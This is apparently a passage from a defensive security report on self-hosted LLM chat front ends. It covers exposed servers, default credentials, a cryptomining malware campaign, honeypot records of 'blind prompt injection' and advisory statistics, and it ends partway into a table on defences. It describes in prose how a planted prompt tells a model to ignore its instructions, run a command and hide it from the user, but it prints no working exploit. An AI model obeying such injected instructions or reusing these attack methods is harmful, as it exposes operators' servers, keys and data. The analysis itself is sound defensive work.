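Cybernews published its findings three months before the withdrawal. SC Media's summary describes nearly all 12,000 servers as susceptible to CVE-2025-63391, as one would expect, since every installation gives the reply that the CVE describes. According to Compare the Cloud's *Compromised server infrastructure and cybersecurity*, Cybernews thought that the address that gives this reply and a second one that returns the version number could help attackers find targets. Neither address lets an attacker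 install anything.

Some databases were slow to reflect the withdrawal. Open WebUI's *CVEdetails* (2026) lists nine withdrawn records, including this one, that the vulnerability site CVEdetails still presented as active on August 8. The site listed another of the nine, CVE-2024-7959, with an estimated 24% chance of exploitation activity within 30 days.

### Percentages of what?

A small group of servers can produce an alarming percentage. Liu and colleagues report that 20.2% of AnythingLLM servers allowed access without a login and that default credentials worked on 60.6% of Dify servers. Both figures leave out most of the live servers in the sample:

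| Finding | Servers | Share of the smaller group | Share of all live servers |
|---|---|---|---|
| AnythingLLM, login apparently off | 48 | 20.2% of 238 that responded | 4.6% of 1,047 |
| Dify, default database password accepted | 217 | 60.6% of 358 with an exposed database port | 3.5% of 6,136 |
| Open WebUI, login off | 35 | 0.8% of 4,448 that responded | 0.6% of 5,896 |

Of the live AnythingLLM servers, 4.6% were open if the 809 that gave no usable response were all protected, and 20.2% were open if those 809 resembled the servers that responded. Liu and colleagues could not check either assumption. They counted a server as open if it returned its list of workspaces, but some servers with a password may also have returned it because of the flaw in AnythingLLM 1.8.5 described earlier.

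On a volunteer's open AnythingLLM server, the researchers could read every user's conversations without logging in. They also had the owner's privileges, including the power to delete workspaces and document collections.

The default password still works on 60.6% of Dify servers with an exposed database port, so an attacker could get in this way on 3.5% of all live Dify servers. The paper's abstract gives only the higher figure and doesn't mention the exposed port.

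### Default credentials

Dify stores its data in PostgreSQL, a database program. In versions up to 1.5.1, every installation started with the same database username and password, which anyone could read in the public source code. This flaw is CVE-2025-56157 and has a severity score of 9.8.

An attacker can use the password only if the database accepts connections from outside. According to Liu and colleagues, the operators of the 358 exposed servers had opened the database port themselves, probably to manage the database remotely. The score of 9.8 is fair for those servers but too high for an installation whose database accepts connections only from Dify.

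Someone who logs in to the database bypasses Dify's permission checks and can read or alter accounts, conversations and the contents of document collections. The default database account is a "superuser", which PostgreSQL allows to run programs on the database's machine. Liu and colleagues used this feature to get a command line on a volunteer's server. If the database runs in its own container, as it usually does with Dify, the attacker at first controls only that container, not the whole machine.

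The researchers connected to the 217 databases, which is stronger evidence than a guess from a version number. Operators can fix the problem by closing the port to the internet and setting a unique password. Once the database exists, they have to change the password in both Dify's settings file and PostgreSQL, because PostgreSQL keeps its own copy.

A default signing key can be as dangerous as a default password, because anyone who knows it can forge a session token for any account. The vulnerability record CVE-2025-15603 reported that Open WebUI had such a key in its code. The record was later withdrawn because, according to the explanation reproduced by Rapid7, every supported way of starting Open WebUI first sets or generates a different key. An operator who starts the underlying server program directly, which Open WebUI does not support, would still get the default key.

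Wiz saw attackers use the default master key of LiteLLM, a gateway that forwards requests to many model providers. If an operator connects Open WebUI to such a gateway, anyone with the master key can bypass Open WebUI and its permission settings.

### Cryptocurrency mining on open servers

*Attacker exploits misconfigured AI tool to run AI-generated payload* (Hernandez and Rizzo, 2025) describes an attack on a customer of the security company Sysdig. The customer had accidentally exposed an Open WebUI server to the internet without a login, and every visitor had administrator rights.

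The attacker added a Tool, which by design runs as Python code on the server. The Tool was one of Open WebUI's standard templates with malicious code added at the end under 64 layers of encoding. Hernandez and Rizzo think the attacker probably installed it with a script instead of through the web page, which would make the attack easy to repeat on other servers.

On Linux, the code downloaded two cryptocurrency miners and set up a system service to restart them. It gave the service a name resembling PyTorch, a common machine-learning package, and hid the miners from the usual lists of running programs. It also sent the attacker a description of the machine, including its graphics processors, through the chat service Discord.

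On Windows, the code also installed programs that steal credentials from Chrome browser extensions and from Discord. This could matter to someone trying Open WebUI on an ordinary PC, where the browser holds passwords unrelated to the application. Only one or two of about 70 antivirus scanners flagged each of three main components of the malware.

The attacker doesn't seem to have earned much. One of the two cryptocurrency wallets held about $700, though the other's balance is unknown. Since the victims pay for the hardware and electricity, an automated attack can be profitable even when it earns that little.

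Sysdig's title refers to an "AI-generated" program, but the evidence for this is modest. The code's style was typical of language models, and a detection tool estimated an 85% to 90% chance of heavy AI assistance. Such tools can be wrong, and the researchers found that a person had written some of the code. The attack would have worked as well without AI because the server was open.

Cybernews later described a longer campaign. ThreatCluster's *OpenWebUI* dates the news to March 19, 2026, and the campaign's start to late 2024. Cybernews found 14 versions of the malware, all from the same source. These versions used the same kind of layered encoding as the program Sysdig had analysed, and also reported new victims through Discord. SC Media adds that earlier versions loaded the credential stealer from a Java file, as Sysdig's sample did, and that later ones included it in the Python code. Sysdig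 therefore probably saw one attack from this campaign, although the press accounts don't say so.

Cybernews found that 45 of the 98 servers without a login were compromised. Another 33 had configuration conflicts and system errors, and 11 worked normally with no sign of an intruder. The accounts don't include the status of the remaining nine. TechRadar's *Multiple OpenWebUI AI servers infected with cryptominers and infostealers stayed up* says in its opening summary that the 33 faulty servers also showed signs of compromise, but the body of the article describes only errors.

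The compromised servers make up 46% of those without a login, 80% of those that Cybernews could clearly classify as compromised or clean, and less than 0.4% of the 12,000 servers online. An operator who has left the login off should therefore assume that an attacker has already found the server. These figures are of little use for estimating the risk to an installation with its login on.

The more than 2,000 servers with open registration are harder to assess. By default, a stranger who registers can't run code, because new accounts need approval and creating Tools needs a further permission. It would be wrong to add these servers to the 98, because the number of operators who had changed both settings is unknown.

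### Injected prompts on decoy servers

Researchers at Wiz looked for attack methods other than installing malware as a plugin on an open server. They ran honeypots, which are decoy servers that record what intruders do. Wiz's *Inside 90 days of attacks on AI infrastructure* (August 2026) reports, among other findings, attempts to attack applications through their models.

The attackers sent prompts to Open WebUI, LangChain, the agent builder Flowise and the automation program Node-RED, trying to make a model use one of its tools to run an operating-system command. They couldn't see the command's output, so they had the command contact a host name they had made up for each server. They controlled the DNS records for these names, so they could tell from a lookup that the command had run.

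Wiz calls this technique "blind prompt injection". Wiz did not capture the prompts, so it reconstructed their likely form from the programs that ran on the decoys and from published examples of prompt injection. The reconstructed prompt tells the model to ignore its earlier instructions, run the command and not mention it to the user.

This is good evidence that attackers now try prompt injection against self-hosted applications, but it doesn't show how often they succeed, because Wiz doesn't count attempts or successes for each application. The successful sessions Wiz describes ended with a cryptocurrency miner in Node-RED's folder, and it reports no such result for Open WebUI. Node-RED can also run commands without a model, so the missing prompts leave some doubt about how the attackers got into it.

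The technique also needs a model that can run commands. An Open WebUI model that only answers questions would at most reply with text about the command. The attackers appear to have sent their prompts directly to servers they could reach, so the honeypots provide no evidence about indirect injection through documents.

### Model gateways and backends

Attackers have done more visible damage to the components behind the front end than to the front end itself. One such component, a LiteLLM gateway, can hold an organisation's keys for OpenAI, Anthropic and other providers, so one successful attack can expose them all.

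Wiz saw attackers exploit two flaws in LiteLLM's support for MCP tool servers. CVE-2026-59822 let a caller use the tool-server gateway with any token, even a single letter. CVE-2026-42271 was in a function for testing a tool server's settings before saving them. The function ran any command the caller supplied, nearly the same mistake LibreChat had made. The attackers' command started a miner and then replied as a genuine tool server would, so the test appeared to succeed.

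After breaking in, some attackers read LiteLLM's master key from the running program's memory, where a search of the disk would not find it. In the same sessions, they checked which models the gateway could reach, for example by asking a model for its name. An intruder who finds an expensive model can use it or resell access to it at the operator's expense.

Marr reports that 518 of the models on the Ollama servers Intruder examined in its scan passed requests on to commercial models from companies such as Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. An Ollama server doesn't keep conversations, so a stranger may find no private text there, but can still run up a bill for the owner.

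The largest campaign also targeted gateways and backends. Its malware has infected more than 3,400 servers since April 2026, according to findings by the threat-research team Black Lotus Labs, reported in *Cryptomining botnet hides C2 addresses in GitHub poem, infects over 3,400 servers* (Markovic, 2026). Most of the servers appeared to run vulnerable versions of software such as LiteLLM and Ollama. In the sample the team analysed, the attacker used the LiteLLM function affected by CVE-2026-42271.

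Infected servers mine cryptocurrency and search for more victims. They find the attacker's control server by reading a poem on GitHub, in which four words stand for the four numbers of an IP address. The attacker switches to a new control server by changing the words, so blocking one address stops the malware only briefly.

From May, the attacker scanned mostly for port 3000, the default for the document converter Gotenberg, and port 4000, the default for LiteLLM. AnythingLLM and other front ends often use port 3000 too, so the attacker probably contacted many of them. Markovic lists no front ends among the victims. An attack written for Gotenberg would fail against AnythingLLM, but the attacker could later add an attack that targets a front end.

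### Has anyone stolen or poisoned documents?

These attackers wanted computing power, credentials and access to paid models. No account of the attacks describes an intruder copying a workspace's documents, planting a false document or rewriting a stored prompt. The known cases of document theft from a self-hosted front end are demonstrations by researchers, such as the test on a volunteer's AnythingLLM server.

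A Tool on an Open WebUI server can read the database, so the intruders who controlled the 45 compromised servers could have read every chat and document on them. Researchers came across private material without looking for it. Marr describes a chatbot whose conversation history was open to any visitor, and Flowise servers that exposed a business's prompts and workflows.

Theft of documents would also be harder to notice than mining. A miner keeps the processors busy and connects to known mining services, so Sysdig's software could detect one. An intruder who reads documents through the search function leaves little more than a few extra requests in the log, and the operator may not keep a log. A false document uploaded by an intruder may look like any other upload, and an employee who gets a wrong answer from it is likely to blame the model.

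Honeypots are poor at detecting either kind of attack. A decoy has no real salary file to steal and no employees to mislead, so an attacker interested in a particular firm has no reason to visit it. The lack of public cases therefore suggests only that automated attacks on strangers' servers have mostly been about money. An operator who finds a miner on a front end's server should still treat the chats, documents and keys stored there as stolen, because the intruder could have copied them.

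## Which of these risks exist only because there is a language model?

The attackers who put cryptocurrency miners on open servers did it by adding a plugin, which the servers would have run even without a language model. The email that made GPT-4o send away a user's SSH keys would have done nothing without a model to act on it.

The same comparison works as a test for any attack. A tester replaces the model that writes the answers, leaves the accounts, documents, tools and web page as they are, and tries the attack again. The replacement can be an ordinary search box, which shows the passages that match a query, or a program that gives a fixed reply, such as "Thank you for your question". If the attack works as before, the model is irrelevant to it. If it still works but does less harm or takes more effort, the model was making it worse. If it fails with both replacements, it needs a model.

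Hashemi Natanzi and Tang use a similar criterion in their survey, which covers an ordinary software flaw only if the model changes how an attacker reaches it or what harm it does.

| Case | What happens without the model | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Script in a stored prompt | The script runs when a user inserts the prompt, before any model receives it | Unchanged |
| Taking over a prompt's record in LibreChat | The database still accepts the extra fields | Unchanged |
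| Crafted file names, archives and PDFs | The server handles the file before any model reads it | Unchanged |
| Importing a page from an internal machine | The server still fetches the page and returns its text | Unchanged |
| Searching a colleague's restricted file | A search box with the same missing check returns the same passages | Unchanged |
| Commands in tool-server settings | LibreChat runs the command when the user saves the settings | Unchanged |
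| Script from a hostile model server | The attacker's server can send the script without running a model | Unchanged |
| System prompt included in the list of models | The server itself sends the text to the browser | Unchanged |
| Mining on an open server | The server runs the plugin without consulting a model | Unchanged |
| False claim in a document | A search box shows the claim beside the real policy, and the reader chooses | Worse with a model |
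| Script in a model's answer | A search box can pass on only a script that a document already contains | Worse with a model |
| New system prompt on an open Ollama server | An intruder could change a fixed reply too, but one instruction to a model can alter the answers to every question | Worse with a model |
| Break-in at a model gateway | The intruder still gets the server, but no paid models to use or resell | Worse with a model |
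| Document that makes the model refuse to answer | A search box still lists the other documents | Needs a model |
| Secret coaxed out of a system prompt | No program repeats the prompt, so questions can't bring it out | Needs a model |
| Private text in a picture's address | Nothing copies the text into the address | Needs a model |
| Email that makes an agent run a script | A search box displays the instruction and does not act on it | Needs a model |

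The table lists leaks of a system prompt twice, because only one of the two needs a model.

### Cases that are hard to place

A script in a model's answer is hard to classify because both the page and the model contribute to the attack. The page has the usual XSS flaw of inserting text from elsewhere as HTML. If a hotel's brochure contained the script, a search page with the same flaw would run it too. But with a model, the attacker can also write a plain description of what the script should do and leave the model to produce the code. A filter that checks uploads for scripts would miss this. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* compares this to giving users indirect access to additional functions, because whoever controls the prompt can influence the output. The fix is the same as for XSS on any other web page.

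GitLab's *Advisories for Pypi/Open-Webui package* describes an Open WebUI flaw that is even harder to classify. A chat message can include a picture. If the picture's address didn't look like a web address or embedded picture data, the server treated it as the identifier of a stored file. The server read that file without checking who owned it and sent it to the model, and the attacker could then ask the model about the contents. If a fixed reply replaced the model's answer, the attacker would learn nothing, so this attack needs a model. But adding the missing ownership check ends the attack whatever model is in use, so an attack can depend on a model even when the code that needs repair is elsewhere.

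Open WebUI's chat page also accepted messages from other websites that could fill in and submit a prompt. GitLab notes that a hostile site could use this to make the model use tools with the visitor's permissions. The same flaw on a search page would only have let the site make the visitor run a search.

Embedding inversion, in which an attacker reconstructs text from stolen embeddings, depends on the embedding model and not on the model that writes answers. Replacing the embedding model with a keyword index removes this risk because there are no embeddings left to steal.

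Extracting a document by asking questions would even be easier without a model, because a search box would show the chunks word for word.

### The comparison with SQL injection

Most attacks that need a model are forms of prompt injection. The name, coined in 2022, is modelled on SQL injection, one of the best-known flaws in web software. SQL is a language for querying databases. Suppose the engineering firm's website looks up refund limits by city and builds each query by pasting in whatever the visitor typed. A visitor who types SQL instead of a city can change the query, and perhaps read or delete the whole database.

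The standard fix is a parameterised query, in which the program sends the command and the value separately:

```
Command:  SELECT refund_limit FROM hotels WHERE city = ?
Value:    Graz
```

The database works out the structure of the command before it fills in the value, so it treats whatever the visitor types only as a city name.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C argues that developers can't expect a fix for prompt injection equivalent to the one for SQL injection. A model predicts the next token from a single sequence, with no separate places for commands and values. Markers around a document can make the model less likely to follow instructions in it, but they can't guarantee that it won't.

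David C therefore calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that someone with fewer rights tricks into using its rights for them. Developers can usually fix such a program, but David C argues that with a model they can only make the trick less likely and limit the harm it does.

A developer who has SQL injection in mind may look for the one correct way to insert a document, apply it and mistakenly consider the problem solved. SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010, more than a decade after they were first described, when many websites already depended on databases. David C warns that a similar wave of breaches may follow if developers build models into most applications without allowing for prompt injection.

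Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, agree that models lack this separation but keep the comparison. They group prompt injection with buffer overflows, SQL injection and XSS, in all of which software treats an attacker's data as instructions. Developers succeeded against the older attacks by restructuring the software, not by getting better at recognising malicious input. Narisetty and colleagues conclude that ordinary code outside the model has to decide which actions to allow. David C recommends much the same, so the dispute is mainly about whether the analogy helps developers reach that conclusion. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026) calls the analogy useful for describing attacks but a poor guide to preventing them.

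*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026) explains the difference by comparing prompt injection with XSS. An XSS attack depends on the syntax of code, so a program can find the characters it relies on and neutralise them. Prompt injection works through meaning, so the sentence "Disregard the limits in earlier editions" is sound advice in the firm's travel policy but could be an attack in a hotel's brochure.

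*The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026) says the consequences differ too, because SQL injection usually affects only the database, while prompt injection can reach whatever tools and permissions the application gives the model. This somewhat overstates the difference. As David C points out, SQL injection can also let an attacker run code on the database server, and a prompt injection may achieve less than that if the model has no tools.

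Open WebUI has had a conventional injection flaw in its document search. In one configuration of the vector database Milvus, it inserted a collection name from the user's request into a query without escaping (neutralising) characters that have a special meaning there. According to GitLab, this let users bypass the fix for the search flaw CVE-2026-44560. Escaping the name solves that problem, but no equivalent step can make the text of a retrieved document safe for the model.

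*Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems* (2026) suggests that models might one day separate instructions from data, perhaps with special tokens that mark trusted text. It warns that much security work would remain. Web developers still had trouble with logins, sessions and permissions after they adopted parameterised queries.

### What 295 advisories contain

Shifat and colleagues studied 295 GitHub security advisories from January 2025 to January 2026 that mention language models or related software. They found the advisories by searching for words such as "gpt", "openai", "ollama" and "mcp". About a fifth of the flaws had no fix when the researchers collected the data.

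The advisories cited 99 weakness types from the CWE catalogue. Code injection was the most common, with 24 occurrences, followed by command injection and unsafe deserialisation with 22 each. Deserialisation turns stored data back into program objects and, if done unsafely, can run an attacker's code. Cross-site scripting appeared 19 times, path traversal 18 times and SQL injection 11 times. Shifat and colleagues found no new class of coding mistake specific to language models.

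A CWE label describes the mistake in the code but not the model's part in an attack, so the researchers added risk labels from OWASP's 2025 Top 10 for LLM Applications.

They first sorted the 133 affected packages with their own removal test, calling a package "LLM-associated" if it would lose its purpose without language models. They put 84 packages in this group. Another 16, such as Milvus, are common in language-model systems but also useful elsewhere, and the remaining 33 had little to do with language models. The researchers then randomly sampled 100 of the 260 advisories for the first two groups, and two researchers independently labelled each one.

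| OWASP risk (2025 name) | What it covers | Advisories, out of 100 | Rank in 2025 | Rank in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | Input that changes the model's behaviour in unintended ways | 18 | 1 | 1 |
| Sensitive information disclosure | Exposure of private data | 17 | 2 | 2 |
| Supply chain | Compromised or flawed libraries, models, data or tools | 44 | 3 | 4 |
| Data and model poisoning | Manipulated training data or embeddings | 7 | 4 | 5 |
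| Improper output handling | Use of the model's output without checking it | 12 | 5 | 10 |
| Excessive agency | More freedom or permissions than the model should have | 20 | 6 | 3 |
| System prompt leakage | Exposure of sensitive standing instructions | 0 | 7 | 8 |
| Vector and embedding weaknesses | Faulty handling of embeddings | 1 | 8 | 9 |
| Misinformation | False answers that seem credible | 0 | 9 | 7 |
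| Unbounded consumption | Uncontrolled use that exhausts the server or runs up a bill | 17 | 10 | 6 |

The counts add up to more than 100 because 37 advisories had more than one label. Seven were labelled with prompt injection, improper output handling and excessive agency. In one of these, the attacker's text influences the input that the model passes to a tool, and the tool uses that input in a command without the application checking it.

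Some advisories fitted none of the ten risks. Of the advisories, 63 had one label and 37 had at least two, including seven with at least three, so there should be at least 144 labels in total. The counts for the ten risks add up to only 136, so at least eight advisories must have gone into the "miscellaneous" category.

The supply-chain figure of 44 is less informative than it looks because most of the packages are libraries or tools that other software builds on, so almost any flaw in one can count as a supply-chain risk. *Understanding the Supply Chain and Risks of Large Language Model Applications* (Ma, Quan and colleagues, 2025) reports a similar pattern, with 1,229 recorded issues in libraries and 50 in applications. The two numbers aren't directly comparable, though, because the library issues came from a vulnerability database and the application issues from user discussions.

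Before settling their disagreements, Shifat's two annotators had a Cohen's kappa of 0.76 and a Gwet's AC1 of 0.95. Both scores correct the observed rate of agreement for chance:

```
score = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)
```

Kappa and AC1 differ in how they estimate chance agreement. If two people decide whether a label fits each of 100 advisories, they might both say yes to 8, both say no to 88, and disagree on 4, with each saying yes to 10. Their observed agreement is 0.96. Kappa estimates chance agreement as 0.1 × 0.1 + 0.9 × 0.9, or 0.82, which gives a score of 0.78. AC1 estimates it as 2 × 0.1 × 0.9, or 0.18, which gives 0.95. The real scores are close to these, as expected when most labels are rare. Kappa is the more cautious measure because it gives less credit for agreeing that a rare label doesn't apply.

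The sample is small. If random sampling were the only source of error, prompt injection's share of the 260 advisories would probably be between 12% and 24%.

What the researchers counted is a larger problem for judging front ends. Their keyword search missed advisories that don't mention a language model, even if they concern software built around one. Many of the packages, such as the model server vLLM and the programming framework LangChain, aren't front ends. Advisories also record defects in code, and when a model gives a wrong answer based on a false brochure, there is no faulty line of code to correct. The counts of zero for misinformation and system prompt leakage may therefore reflect what people report more than how often these problems occur. For the same reason, the finding of no new class of weakness applies only to code, not to the behaviour of models.

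### When votes and incidents disagree

OWASP (2026) published a new edition of its list in August. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a vote among practitioners counted for three-quarters of the ranking, and incidents from public vulnerability databases counted for one-quarter. OWASP collected 7,714 incidents, of which 6,639 had enough detail to classify.

Practitioners voted prompt injection the greatest risk, but it would not have made the top ten based on incidents alone. OWASP, quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*, says that fewer clear cases reach a public database because "teams fight injection hard". That may be true, but the count would also be low if prompt injection seldom did much harm or if victims had no reason to file a vulnerability report about it, and the incident data can't distinguish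 between these explanations.

Misinformation showed the opposite pattern, ranking low in the vote but high in the incident data. Shifat and colleagues found no case of it in 100 advisories. Such a large difference suggests that these rankings depend strongly on which records are used and how they are labelled.

### Counting one front end's flaws

Ecosyste.ms' *Security Advisories for open-webui in pypi* lists 89 Open WebUI advisories from 2026 by title, without CWE numbers. The table below assigns each advisory to one kind of mistake, based on its title and, where the title was unclear, on GitLab's description. The table's CWE numbers are the closest matches, not official labels.

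| Kind of mistake | Closest CWE types | Advisories |
|---|---|---|
| Missing or wrong permission check | CWE-862, CWE-863, CWE-639 | 44 |
| Server-side request forgery (SSRF) and related fetching flaws | CWE-918 | 15 |
| Requests that stall or disrupt the service | CWE-400, CWE-835, CWE-1333 | 8 |
| XSS | CWE-79 | 6 |
| Missing or faulty login and session checks | CWE-287, CWE-306, CWE-613 | 6 |
| Path traversal | CWE-22 | 2 |
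| Unwanted requests triggered by another site | CWE-346, CWE-352 | 2 |
| Other, such as a race condition and mass assignment | Various | 6 |

Problems with permission checks account for 49% of the advisories and SSRF for 17%. Some advisories could go in a different row, but too few to change the order of the first two rows. Radical Notion, a site that compiles vulnerability records, counted 176 CVE records for Open WebUI and lists the same main problems. The four most common types there are missing authorisation, XSS, access through an identifier that the user controls, and SSRF.

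Most of the 89 attacks would work against a front end that gave a fixed reply instead of a model's output. The picture-address flaw is one of the exceptions. No title in the Ecosyste.ms list mentions prompt injection. One mentions system prompt leakage, but it describes the flaw in which the server sent the prompt to the browser.

### Ordinary bugs, or new ways to reach them?

These records are good evidence that self-hosted front ends are ordinary web applications with ordinary bugs. Developers have known for decades how to check permissions and insert text safely, and the mistakes come from doing so inconsistently. According to GitLab's list, Open WebUI included the sanitiser DOMPurify but used it in only 9 of the 23 places where the page inserted HTML. In nearly all the known break-ins, attackers used open logins, default passwords or flaws in conventional code. A firm running a year-old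 version of its front end would therefore reduce its risk more by updating it than by buying a prompt-injection filter.

The argument for treating the model as a separate risk is that it lets more people reach a bug. A supplier without an account can't normally use the firm's tools or put text on an administrator's screen. But once the office manager uploads the supplier's brochure, its text can reach a model that does both with her permissions. An attack can work even if no single part is faulty. For example, an image link can leak private text when the search returns a file the employee is allowed to read, the model writes a valid link and the browser loads it. Advisories usually describe a defect in one package, so they are likely to miss attacks that depend on how working parts interact.

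Seven of the 100 advisories in Shifat's sample have all three labels, so such combinations do occur in real software, but this is modest evidence and the sample covered much more than chat pages. If a front end's model has no tools and its documents all come from staff, ordinary bugs account for most of the risk. They account for much less if the model reads incoming email and can run scripts, because a stranger's email could trigger a script even if the firm installed every update on the day of its release.

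## Which defences work, and how well?

Operators have to choose defences according to the attackers they are worried about. A login keeps strangers from installing a cryptocurrency miner, but it doesn't stop malicious text in a hotel brochure that an employee uploads. Careful instructions to the model may make that text less effective, though they can't protect a database whose password is public.

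### Keeping strangers out

Open WebUI is designed for private, trusted networks, and its defaults make it easy to set up. Its quick-start command for Docker, a program that runs containers, includes `-p 3000:8080`, which makes the chat page available on every network the machine is connected to. A home router normally blocks outsiders, but on a rented server with a public address, anyone can open the page, and the first person to register becomes the administrator. Docker also adds its own firewall rules, so the port can stay open even after the operator blocks it in the server's usual firewall tool.

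Adding an address to the command limits the page to the machine itself:

```
-p 3000:8080              Every network the machine is connected to
-p 127.0.0.1:3000:8080    This machine only
```

Colleagues can then connect through a reverse proxy, a program on the same machine that receives requests and passes them to the front end. The proxy can encrypt the connection and require a login before passing a request on. If it accepts requests only from the firm's private network (VPN), outsiders can't exploit even flaws that need no account, such as the LibreChat test route that returned anyone's chats. Liu and colleagues observe that individuals, research institutions and startups often skip this step because proxies, certificates and a shared login take work to set up.

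A proxy can also introduce a flaw. According to a copy of Open WebUI's documentation hosted by Mintlify, the proxy can identify the logged-in user to the front end by adding a header to each request, and the operator sets that header's name in `WEBUI_AUTH_TRUSTED_EMAIL_HEADER`. Anyone who can reach the front end directly could send the same header and log in as the administrator. The front end must therefore accept connections only from the proxy, and the proxy must delete any such header that arrives from outside.

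The three front ends have different settings for the basic precautions:

| Precaution | Open WebUI | AnythingLLM | LibreChat |
|---|---|---|---|
| Require a login | Leave `WEBUI_AUTH` on | Set `AUTH_TOKEN`, or use multi-user mode | Always required |
| Close registration | `ENABLE_SIGNUP=false` | Multi-user mode, where people join by invitation | `ALLOW_REGISTRATION=false` |
| Replace the secrets that protect sessions | `WEBUI_SECRET_KEY` | `JWT_SECRET` | `JWT_SECRET` and `JWT_REFRESH_SECRET` |
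| Limit who can run code | `ENABLE_PLUGINS=false` | Few administrators and managers | Keep stdio tool servers in `librechat.yaml` |
| Limit addresses the server fetches | `WEB_FETCH_FILTER_LIST` | Leave `COLLECTOR_ALLOW_ANY_IP` off | `actions.allowedDomains` |

An old edition of Open WebUI's *Environment Variable Configuration* lists `t0p-s3cr3t` as the default signing secret outside Docker, so operators should set a long random one. LibreChat's example settings file has also contained ready-made secrets that operators need to replace, including `CREDS_KEY`, which encrypts stored provider keys. Open WebUI saves some settings in its database when it first starts and may then ignore changes to their environment variables. The administrator should therefore check the settings page and try to register from a private browser window to see whether sign-up is open.

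Databases and model backends don't need a public address. Outside a container, Ollama accepts connections only from its own machine unless the operator changes `OLLAMA_HOST`. The front end can reach PostgreSQL, Meilisearch or a vector database over an internal container network without publishing a port.

The evidence for these measures is incomplete. Cybernews found intruders on 45 of 98 Open WebUI servers with the login off, but there is no comparable count for servers with it on, and no published study appears to compare break-ins with and without a VPN. The case for a VPN rests on how the attacks work, since most begin with a request that the VPN would keep from reaching the server.

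### Limiting people who have accounts

A VPN doesn't stop a colleague or someone who has stolen a colleague's laptop. An operator can defend against these attackers by limiting what each account can do.

Administrator accounts need the most protection because a script in a shared chat can use an administrator's session to install a plugin. A small firm usually needs only two administrators, so that one can act when the other is away. Each should have a second, ordinary account for daily work. If an administrator opens a malicious chat from the ordinary account, the script can read that account's chats but can't install anything. Separate accounts cost nothing and also limit the damage from display flaws that nobody has found yet.

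Third-party plugins are a risk even when an administrator installs them deliberately. Open WebUI highlights some community plugins but warns that this doesn't mean they have been vetted, and tells operators to read the source code every time. A plugin can also cause the server to install more Python packages, whose code the administrator probably hasn't read. Operators can turn off these installations with `ENABLE_PIP_INSTALL_FRONTMATTER_REQUIREMENTS`.

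Shorter sessions limit how long a stolen token can be used. Setting `JWT_EXPIRES_IN` to eight hours instead of the default four weeks cuts the maximum by a factor of 84, but users must then log in each working day. Redis lets the server cancel a token when its owner signs out, but for a while this worked only partly, even when Redis was set up exactly as recommended. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-59219* (2026), the server rejected a cancelled token on ordinary requests but still accepted it on live connections, including the one to the terminal. Mondoo's *CVE-2026-59219* lists versions from 0.9.0 until 0.10.0 as affected, with a score of 7.1.

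Logs can show who changed a prompt or downloaded a file, but they won't prevent an attack. According to the documentation copy at Mintlify, `ENABLE_AUDIT_STDOUT` is for recording user actions and `LOG_FORMAT=json` is for sending logs to a separate system. That separation matters because an intruder who controls the front end's server can edit the logs on it. Operators should record complete requests only if they need them, since doing so makes the log another copy of everyone's chats.

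### Containing a break-in

Some attackers will get past the login and the permission checks, so an operator also has to decide what the server can reach. The front end usually needs access to its database, its model backend and perhaps one provider's API, but seldom to the payroll system or a cloud machine's credential service.

The application's own address filters are worth having but have a poor record. According to *CVE-2026-88001*, a page by the security company Miggo, users could get past the operator's list of blocked websites through a redirect if `AIOHTTP_CLIENT_ALLOW_REDIRECTS` was on. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3653* reports that the Playwright page loader did not filter WebSocket connections, which stay open for two-way traffic, or requests from service workers, which are background scripts.

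A firewall outside the application checks the IP address of each connection, so it can block a forbidden address whether the server got there through a redirect, a changed DNS record or a background script. The operator can block all private addresses, 169.254.169.254 and Azure's 168.63.129.16, then allow the few internal services that the front end needs, but those services remain exposed. The test in OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2743* reached an internal port of the Open WebUI container itself, and the same method could reach other containers on its network, so each of them still needs a password.

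Code that users run needs tighter limits. Open WebUI's companion program, Open Terminal, lets a model run commands and handle files. Open WebUI describes putting it on an internal network with no route to the internet, or listing permitted sites in `OPEN_TERMINAL_ALLOWED_DOMAINS`. The container sets up a firewall when it starts, then drops the privilege to change it, so code running inside can't remove the limits. Shorter lists of permitted sites work better. The example list includes github.com, so an attacker could send stolen text to their own GitHub repository.

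Containers should also run without root, but AnythingLLM's standard Docker command adds a broad Linux privilege, `SYS_ADMIN`, which the browser that imports web pages uses for its own sandbox. An operator who never imports web pages can omit this privilege.

Each of these settings needs testing. OSV's *GHSA-482j-2pq6-q5w4* shows that the Jupyter flaw still worked on a server whose settings listed code execution as off.

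### Marking, training and filtering

These measures do little against the hotel brochure, because the office manager is allowed to upload it and the employee is allowed to ask about it. The remaining defences concern what the model does with the text.

One defence is to mark retrieved text so that the model can tell it from instructions. The front end can put a marker at each end of a passage, or insert an unusual character between all its words and tell the model never to obey text in that form. With the second method, an attacker can't end the marked passage early by adding a false end marker. In *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024), Hines, Lopez and colleagues reported that such methods lowered the attack success rate on GPT models from over 50% to under 2%.

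The company that makes a model can also train it to rank instructions, with the operator's system prompt above the user's message and both above retrieved text. *SecAlign*, a 2025 conference paper by Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues, shows one way to do this. The researchers gave open models inputs containing a planted instruction and trained them to prefer an answer that followed the user over one that followed the attacker. Attack success rates fell below 10%, with little loss in ordinary usefulness.

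A detection filter is a separate program, often a small model, that examines text and blocks anything resembling an attack. Filters can wrongly flag genuine documents, because these also contain instructions. Suppose a collection has 10,000 chunks, five of them planted, and a filter catches 90% of planted chunks but also flags 1% of the genuine ones. It would flag about 100 genuine chunks and four or five planted ones, so only about 4% of the flagged chunks would be planted.

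*AgentDojo*, a 2024 test by Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, has a model carry out office tasks such as handling email and payments while tool results contain planted instructions. A filter lowered the attack success rate on GPT-4o from about half to 8%. But when there was no attack, the filter also reduced the share of tasks the model completed from 69% to about 41%.

| Defence | Attack success in the original test | Effect on useful work |
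|---|---|---|
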